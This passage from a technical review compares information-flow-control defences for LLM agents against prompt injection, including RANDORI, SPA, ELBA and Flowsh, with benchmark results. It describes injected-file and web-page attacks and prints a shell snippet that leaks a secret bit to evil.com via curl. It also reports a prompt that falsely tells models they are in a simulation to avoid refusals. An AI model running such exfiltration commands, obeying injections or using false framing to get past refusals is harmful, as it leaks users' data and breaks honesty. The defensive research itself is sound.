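Garby and colleagues wrote their definitions and proofs in Lean, a programming language that checks proofs mechanically. *Formalization of security* (2026) lists several earlier machine-checked proofs of noninterference, including work by Popescu, Hölzl and Nipkow on programs that make random choices. In LLMbda, the random choices are a model's replies, which can become part of the program.

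The proofs cover the interpreter and both versions of TIPNI. The interpreter is a Lean function, and another theorem shows that if it receives replies drawn from the model's distribution, its results have exactly the probabilities given by the formal rules. The proofs use only three axioms, all standard in Lean's logic.

The proofs assume that the model gives each possible reply a fixed probability, which depends only on the current conversation. As long as that is true, the guarantee holds even if the model is gullible or hostile. But the assumption would fail if the model's provider let it remember earlier conversations. A program could then clear a secret conversation, start a public one, and get the secret back with a public label.

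The proofs don't cover the code that contacts the model over the network or the real effects of tools, because LLMbda requires all data sources to be part of the program. If the server that runs the agent automatically restarts it after a crash, the restarts create another untracked retry loop, and each one could reveal another bit.

Developers also have to label every source correctly and put the right checks in every tool. Other agent defences depend on correct setup by developers too. For example, the monitor in *APPA* (2026) relies on the contracts that developers declare for their tools and on any registered functions that clean up data.

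### An agent that practises first

To find out whether an agent could do useful work under these rules, Garby and colleagues wrote one in LLMbda, called RANDORI. Like CaMeL, it follows the dual-LLM pattern and plans in advance.

Retries were the main difficulty. If a program reads an untrusted file and then fails, sending the error to the planner makes the conversation untrusted, and the planner's next program can no longer pay anyone. RANDORI avoids this by having the planner test its program on invented data, where payments do nothing and every file contains the same placeholder sentence. The planner revises the program until it runs without errors or the attempts run out, then writes a final version that runs once on the real data.

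The errors that reach the planner therefore contain no real data, and a failure in a later line can't cause the agent to pay an invoice twice. But the agent can't recover if the final program fails. Practice rounds also don't reveal label violations, so a program can pass every one and still break a tool's policy in the real run.

RANDORI's policies are a simplified subset of CaMeL's, and they show how much depends on the labels. File contents are labeled untrusted, but the published list doesn't label recent transactions that way, even though the sender of a payment normally writes its subject line. The payment-scheduling tool checks that the amount is trusted but doesn't check the recipient. If the user had specified the amount, the agent could schedule an invoice payment to the attacker's account without endorsing anything. The theorems would still hold, because they only guarantee that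 the labels are right when a tool checks them.

### RANDORI on the banking tasks

The test used the same 16 banking tasks and nine attacks as the rerun of CaMeL, again with three repetitions. Garby and colleagues also ran two of the models without endorsement.

| Agent | Model | Solved, no attack | Solved under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| RANDORI | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 281 of 432 | 2 of 432 |
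| RANDORI | Qwen3.7-plus | 36 of 48 | 274 of 432 | 0 of 432 |
| RANDORI | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 257 of 432 | 0 of 432 |
| Without endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 30 of 48 | 260 of 432 | 0 of 432 |
| Without endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 26 of 48 | 243 of 432 | 0 of 432 |

RANDORI did about as well as CaMeL without policy checks and about twice as well as CaMeL with them (18 of 48). Garby and colleagues conclude that they get security "at essentially no utility cost".

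The comparison with CaMeL is not quite fair, because CaMeL was enforcing stricter policies. With MiMo-v2.5, RANDORI solved 13 more runs than CaMeL did with its checks on. Without endorsement, RANDORI solved only 5 fewer, so the other 8 must have a different cause, plausibly its looser policies. The confidence intervals are wide, at about 20 percentage points either way.

On the other hand, RANDORI was at a disadvantage because models are trained on a great deal of Python and no LLMbda, so its prompt has to explain the language. Models also often refused to write code that sends money or changes passwords, so the prompt states that they are in a simulation and no real money is involved, which would be false if a real bank deployed the agent.

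### The two successful attacks

Both successes came from the same combination of task and attack. The user asks the agent to read a text file and make the payment it describes, but the attacker has replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Because the payment details will come from an untrusted file, the planner writes code that endorses them, and the agent pays the attacker.

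Labels can't distinguish a genuine bill from a forged one here, because both arrive through the same tool with the same label. The user has asked for a payment that depends on whichever bill is in the file, so a tracker can only allow all payments based on the file or refuse them all. Without endorsement, RANDORI refuses them, which stops the attack but makes the task impossible.

Other systems fail in similar places. One of CaMeL's two published failures was a payment of this kind, and the other was the quoted hotel review. TACIT, a system by Odersky and colleagues that tracks an agent's permissions with Scala's type system, failed for the same reason as the hotel review in one of 1,926 trials across all four AgentDojo environments.

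Two successes in 1,296 attacked runs is a rate of about 0.15%, but an attacker wouldn't choose a task at random. Both successes were on this pair, in two of GPT-5.2's three runs. Labels could matter in only 423 of the attacked runs, spread over 47 pairs. Even for the two models that resisted every attack, the 95% confidence interval for the true success rate on those pairs extends to 7.6%.

The banking suite also tests little of what the theorems guarantee. None of its attacks uses branches, retries or crashes to leak a secret, so CaMeL got a perfect security score despite its leaks.

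## SPA and Flowsh: tracking whole plans and whole commands

LLMbda follows every operation in an agent's code, but it requires models to write in a language they have had little training on. A tracker can instead avoid following string operations, either by restricting agents to plans that contain none or by putting a single label on everything a program does during a run.

### Checking a plan before it runs

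*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) restricts what a plan can contain. As in CaMeL, a planning model writes the whole plan before any tool runs. But the plan is a list of steps instead of Python, with only six kinds of step: fetch a stored result, call a tool, ask a quarantined model, show something to the user, branch, and loop. The language has no arithmetic, string templates or functions, so the planner can't write `"DE" + number` and the checker doesn't need a rule for it.

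Each step gets the label

$$\ell_{\text{step}}=pc\;\sqcup\;\bigsqcup_j \ell_{x_j},$$

the join of the program-counter label and the labels of all the variables the step uses. A tool's policy states which labels it accepts. Its result gets the step's label joined with a fixed label for that tool, which for a mail tool would include "untrusted". An answer from the quarantined model simply gets the step's label.

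Here is a plan for the invoice example, written in Python style:

```python
supplier = find_supplier("Acme")
email = get_last_email("Acme")
answer = quarantined_model("Has Acme changed banks?", email)
if answer.changed == True:
    pay(supplier.second_account, 900)
else:
    pay(supplier.first_account, 900)
```

| Step | Program-counter label | Variables used | Label of the step |
|---|---|---|---|
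| `find_supplier` | trusted | none | trusted |
| `get_last_email` | trusted | none | trusted, but its result is untrusted |
| `quarantined_model` | trusted | `email`, untrusted | untrusted |
| `pay` in either branch | untrusted, from `answer` | `supplier`, trusted | untrusted |

The payment tool requires a trusted label, so SPA rejects the plan before opening the e-mail. The rejection depends only on the plan and the labels, so it reveals nothing about the data, unlike a policy violation in the middle of a CaMeL run. SPA also has no retry loop like CaMeL's, because it never asks the planner for a corrected plan.

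### Variables assigned on the branch not taken

CaMeL lets a payment through when the program sets a default account and then skips the line that would replace it. SPA's planner can't write that program, because a plan may assign each variable only once and a variable assigned inside a branch disappears when the branch ends. The checker therefore doesn't have to work out what an untaken branch might have changed. The same restrictions rule out Fenton's program.

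These rules look sound for a single request, but Girrens and Wang don't prove a noninterference theorem. The rules may also leave a gap when SPA keeps results for later requests. The next planner can't read a stored result, but it receives a description of it, such as "details of the Acme invoice". SPA stores results only if the plan finishes, so an e-mail that makes a step fail changes the list of descriptions that the next planner is given. That list has no label. If SPA also stores results from inside branches, the list reveals which branch ran.

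The stored results keep their labels. If the agent saves an invoice on Monday and on Tuesday the user asks it to pay the invoice, the account number is still labeled untrusted.

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo with GPT-5.4 nano. Without label checks, the agent completed 53.0% of tasks, and four of 949 attacks succeeded. All four were on banking task 12, the task for which CaMeL's planner wrote an "interpreter loop". With the checks, no attack succeeded, but the agent completed only 29.0% of tasks. The checks rejected about 53% of all plans, usually because the plan passed one tool's untrusted output to another tool as an argument.

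SPA has no endorsement, so it can't allow any of these. It also checks all of a tool's arguments together, so an untrusted reference text blocks a payment even if the account number is trusted.

In a version of the benchmark that spreads each task over several requests, the checks lowered the completion rate from 62.5% to 35.3%. The reported attack rate was 0.2%, or about two runs. Girrens and Wang describe two travel runs that AgentDojo counted as successful attacks even though SPA had rejected the plan.

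### One floating label for running code

SPA's planner must commit to a plan before it sees any data, whereas the agent in *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) can read data before it writes code. The paper's system, ELBA, appears to be the one that Garby and colleagues cite as TypeGuard. Its agents write Haskell, where a program's type shows what effects the program may have. If the developer asks for a program of a restricted type, the type checker rejects any code that writes a file or opens a connection except through the approved functions.

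ELBA relies on LIO, an existing Haskell library, for information flow control. *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions* (Stefan, Russo and colleagues, 2012) describes LIO, which keeps one *current label* for a running computation and everything in its scope. Reading a web page raises the current label to include the page's label. LIO allows a write only if the current label may flow to the destination, so a program that reads a page from an untrusted site and then tries to write to a trusted destination stops with an error.

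*On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems* (Buiras, Stefan and Russo, 2015) points out that this makes implicit flows trivial to handle, because the condition of every branch already has the current label. FIDES's context label handles the if-statement in the invoice example the same way.

The drawback is label creep. After a program reads a secret, it can't write even the constant 42 to a public channel. LIO addresses this with a function called `toLabeled`, which runs part of the program separately and then restores the old current label. The result comes back sealed under a label the program chose in advance. If the separate part has read anything more restricted than that label allows, LIO stops it.

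ELBA uses `toLabeled` to run subagents. A subagent can read an untrusted page and write a message, and the main agent can send the sealed message without reading it. This resembles the dual-LLM pattern, except that the subagent can also have tools. LIO blocks the dangerous tools once the subagent has read something untrusted.

Zhou and colleagues prove that if the type system guarantees a property for all well-typed programs, the property still holds when an agent writes part of the program. The theorem extends LIO's guarantees to model-written code and the loop around it, without adding new ones. ELBA retries only after type errors, which occur before the new code has called any tools, so an attacker can't read a secret through a series of failed runs, as they can in CaMeL.

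With its policies on, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks, depending on the model, while CaMeL completed 4 to 6. The two systems enforce different policies, so the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the design. ELBA also took about three times as long, because it calls the model again whenever it needs to respond to data.

Ordinary AgentDojo attacks failed against both systems even without policies, so Zhou and colleagues simulated the worst case, in which a subagent obeys any injection it reads. With policies, ELBA resisted all 735 attacks on each of four models, compared with 425 to 621 without them. The policies also lowered the number of tasks completed under attack from 494–558 to 294–351.

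### One label for a whole shell command

Coding agents do much of their work in a *shell*, a program that runs typed commands. One command can start a Python script, a compiler and a download, and no agent framework can read the source code of all these programs. *FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) labels the whole command based on its inputs, without tracking what happens inside it.

Flowsh runs each command in a sandbox, where it can reach the outside world only through files and a network proxy. A monitor in the Linux kernel records every file that any process in the command opens for reading. The command's label is then

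$$\ell_{\text{command}}=\ell_{\text{context}}\sqcup\ell_{\text{arguments}}\sqcup\bigsqcup_{f}\ell_f\sqcup\bigsqcup_{e}\ell_e,$$

where $f$ ranges over the files opened and $e$ over the servers contacted. Everything the command prints, and every file it creates or changes, gets this label. If the monitor loses a record, Flowsh assumes the worst and gives the command the most restrictive label.

Suppose an agent has read a malicious web page, so its context is untrusted and public, (U, L). The page tells it to disguise the company's salary list:

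```sh
base64 salaries.csv | rev > notes.txt
```

This encodes the file as letters and digits, reverses each line and saves the result. In this example, the two programs themselves count as trusted and public.

| Event | Label of the command |
|---|---|
| The command starts | (U, L), from the agent's context |
| `base64` opens `salaries.csv`, which is (T, H) | (U, H) |
| `base64` encodes the text and `rev` reverses it | (U, H) |
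| The command ends | (U, H), which Flowsh stores with `notes.txt` |

The label rises when `base64` opens the file, and nothing the command does afterwards can lower it. Unlike a labelled string class, Flowsh doesn't inspect the text, so it has no string rules that could be wrong. It also covers branches inside the command, because a program can't branch on a file's contents without opening the file.

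### Stored labels, staged writes and network requests

Flowsh stores each file's label in the file's metadata, next to details such as its owner. The label survives a restart and applies under every name the file has, and commands in the sandbox can't change it. If a new session with a clean context tries to upload `notes.txt`, the upload command's label becomes (U, H) as soon as it opens the file. In the published configuration, a file without a stored label counts as untrusted and readable only by the user, so a missing label causes a refusal instead of a leak.

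Flowsh can lose a label when data passes through a server, because it gives everything from one server the same label. In the evaluation, responses from nearly all servers counted as public. If the agent uploaded a private file to GitHub with permission and later downloaded it, the file would be labelled public.

Flowsh first holds a command's changes in a separate layer that only the command can see. When the command ends, Flowsh checks the command's label against the policy for each changed file. For example, an untrusted command may change ordinary project files but not `.bashrc`, which runs whenever the user opens a shell. If any change breaks the policy, the user approves or rejects all of them together, because applying only some could leave the project in a broken state.

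A network request can't be taken back, so the proxy checks it before sending it. The proxy even checks requests that only fetch a page, since the address can contain a secret. If the policy forbids a request, the command gets an error and continues, and the agent can ask the user to allow that destination next time.

The evaluated policy allows a request if the data is public, if the destination may read it, or if the command's label is trusted. So if no untrusted data were involved, Flowsh would let the agent send the salary list anywhere without asking. FIDES makes the same assumption about the user's wishes. A developer can remove the exception for trusted commands, but Flowsh would then ask for approval more often.

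### Fenton's program in four commands

A command's label covers every branch inside it, but the next command starts again from the agent's context. Flowsh relabels only files that a command actually changes, which is the rule that fails in Fenton's program. By the published rules, an attacker could spread that program over several commands. Here `bit.txt` is secret and contains 0 or 1:

```sh
echo true > y; echo true > z
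if grep -q 1 bit.txt; then echo false > y; fi
if grep -q true y; then echo false > z; fi
curl "https://evil.com/?bit=$(cat z)"
```

Each line is a separate command, and `grep -q` tests whether a file contains some text.

| Command | If the secret is 1 | If the secret is 0 |
|---|---|---|
| First | `y` and `z` are true, public | `y` and `z` are true, public |
| Second | `y` becomes false, secret | `y` is still true, public |
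| Third | reads a secret file, but leaves `z` true and public | `z` becomes false, public |
| Fourth | sends "true" | sends "false" |

Stealing a 20-bit bank balance would take 23 commands, because the second command can test all the bits at once but each bit needs its own version of the third.

This attack works only if the agent's context stays public throughout. If the model reads the second command's output, even an empty result, its context should become secret, and the last request fails. But an agent that leaves results in variables to avoid label creep, as FIDES does, would keep its context public. Kim and colleagues don't prove noninterference, which would rule the attack out, and their tests don't include it.

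Buiras and colleagues show the same leak in a version of LIO with changeable labels, and their fix suggests one for Flowsh. In their fix, a program declares which variables a block may change. LIO raises the labels of all those variables before the block reads the secret, and forbids changes to any others. An agent could list the files that a command may change, and Flowsh would then relabel every file on the list, whether or not the command changed it. The second command above would make `y` secret in both cases, and the third would do the same to `z`.

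### Approvals, completed tasks and attacks

Kim and colleagues tested Flowsh with GPT-6.2 Sol on 17 office tasks of their own ("knowledge tasks") and on the 89 tasks of Terminal-Bench, a benchmark of command-line work. They ran every task three times. The table shows the results with a simulated user who approves every harmless request.

| Defence | Knowledge tasks completed | Approvals per completed task | Terminal-Bench tasks completed | Approvals per completed task |
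|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lax sandbox | 96.1% | 6.7 | 77.5% | 9.7 |
| Standard sandbox | 76.5% | 5.7 | 64.4% | 10.0 |
| Strict sandbox | 47.1% | 0.0 | 1.9% | 0.0 |
| Labels on the agent's context only | 60.8% | 1.8 | 67.8% | 9.4 |
| Flowsh | 88.2% | 1.2 | 67.8% | 0.4 |

Compared with the lax sandbox, Flowsh cut approvals per completed task by a factor of 5.8 on the knowledge tasks and 22.5 on Terminal-Bench, but its completion rates were 7.9 and 9.7 percentage points lower, respectively. The reduction in approvals is large partly because the lax sandbox allows everything, so every shell command needed approval, even one that only read a file. A product that doesn't require approval for obviously safe commands would have a lower baseline.

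No attack succeeded against any of the defences in this setting, because the simulated user recognised every attack. In a more informative test without a user, Kim and colleagues gave the attacker full control of the model's output as soon as the model read an injection. The attacks tried to overwrite protected files or send private data to an outside server. All 51 succeeded against the lax sandbox, 3 of 39 against the standard one and none of 40 against Flowsh.

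Without anyone to approve requests, Flowsh completed 58.8% of the knowledge tasks. It completed all 24 runs of tasks whose data was either all trusted or all public, but only 6 of the 27 runs that combined untrusted data with secrets. With the simulated user, it completed 21 of those 27. Tasks such as comparing a private project with papers from the web need both untrusted data and secrets.

Some of the lost tasks failed for reasons unrelated to labels. Flowsh doesn't support background processes that outlive a command, direct communication between commands, or UDP, the network protocol behind many DNS lookups and newer web connections. The sandbox blocks these channels, which limits functionality but doesn't weaken security. On Terminal-Bench, 21 of Flowsh's 86 failed runs needed a background process such as a server. The label rule ignores timing, so a command could leak information about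 a secret by delaying a later public request by an amount that depends on it.

Flowsh added roughly 0.35 to 0.9 seconds to each command in a speed test, and whole tasks took 17–34% longer.

### Coarse labels and finer ones

Flowsh over-taints in several ways. It treats opening a file as reading all of it. It doesn't track the order of file accesses, so if a command writes a public report and then opens a secret file, Flowsh marks the report secret. If one command copies a salary list and then a blank template, Flowsh marks both copies secret.

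*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) would keep those two copies apart. Its monitor records which files each process has read and passes that history along when one process feeds another. Within a process, it only approximates data flow, so a script that reads one file and writes another transfers the label even if the two are unrelated. On two coding benchmarks, Tether wrongly blocked 2.3% and 5.0% of harmless runs, excluding those that involved things it can't trace, such as background services. These figures are hard to compare with Flowsh's because the tasks and policies differ. *ActPlane* (2026) also labels whole files and processes, which is less precise than following individual bytes but avoids the overhead.

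Finer tracking within a program would avoid more false alarms, but it needs separate tools for each programming language and brings back the need for correct rules for every string operation and branch. It may also be unnecessary. *From Fine- to Coarse-Grained Dynamic Information Flow Control and Back* (Vassena, Russo and colleagues, 2022) proves that a tracker with one label per computation can be as precise as one with a label per variable. It gives an automatic translation between the two, both of which satisfy termination-insensitive noninterference. The coarse tracker needs an operation like `toLabeled` to limit how far a label spreads, and the program has to be divided into small enough parts.

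An agent using Flowsh can split its work into separate commands. If it copies the salary list in one command and the template in another, the template stays public. This doesn't help when a single program reads both files, unless someone rewrites that program as several smaller ones. Splitting also gives an attacker more commands over which to spread Fenton's program, so Flowsh would need to fix its file labels before an agent could safely rely on it.
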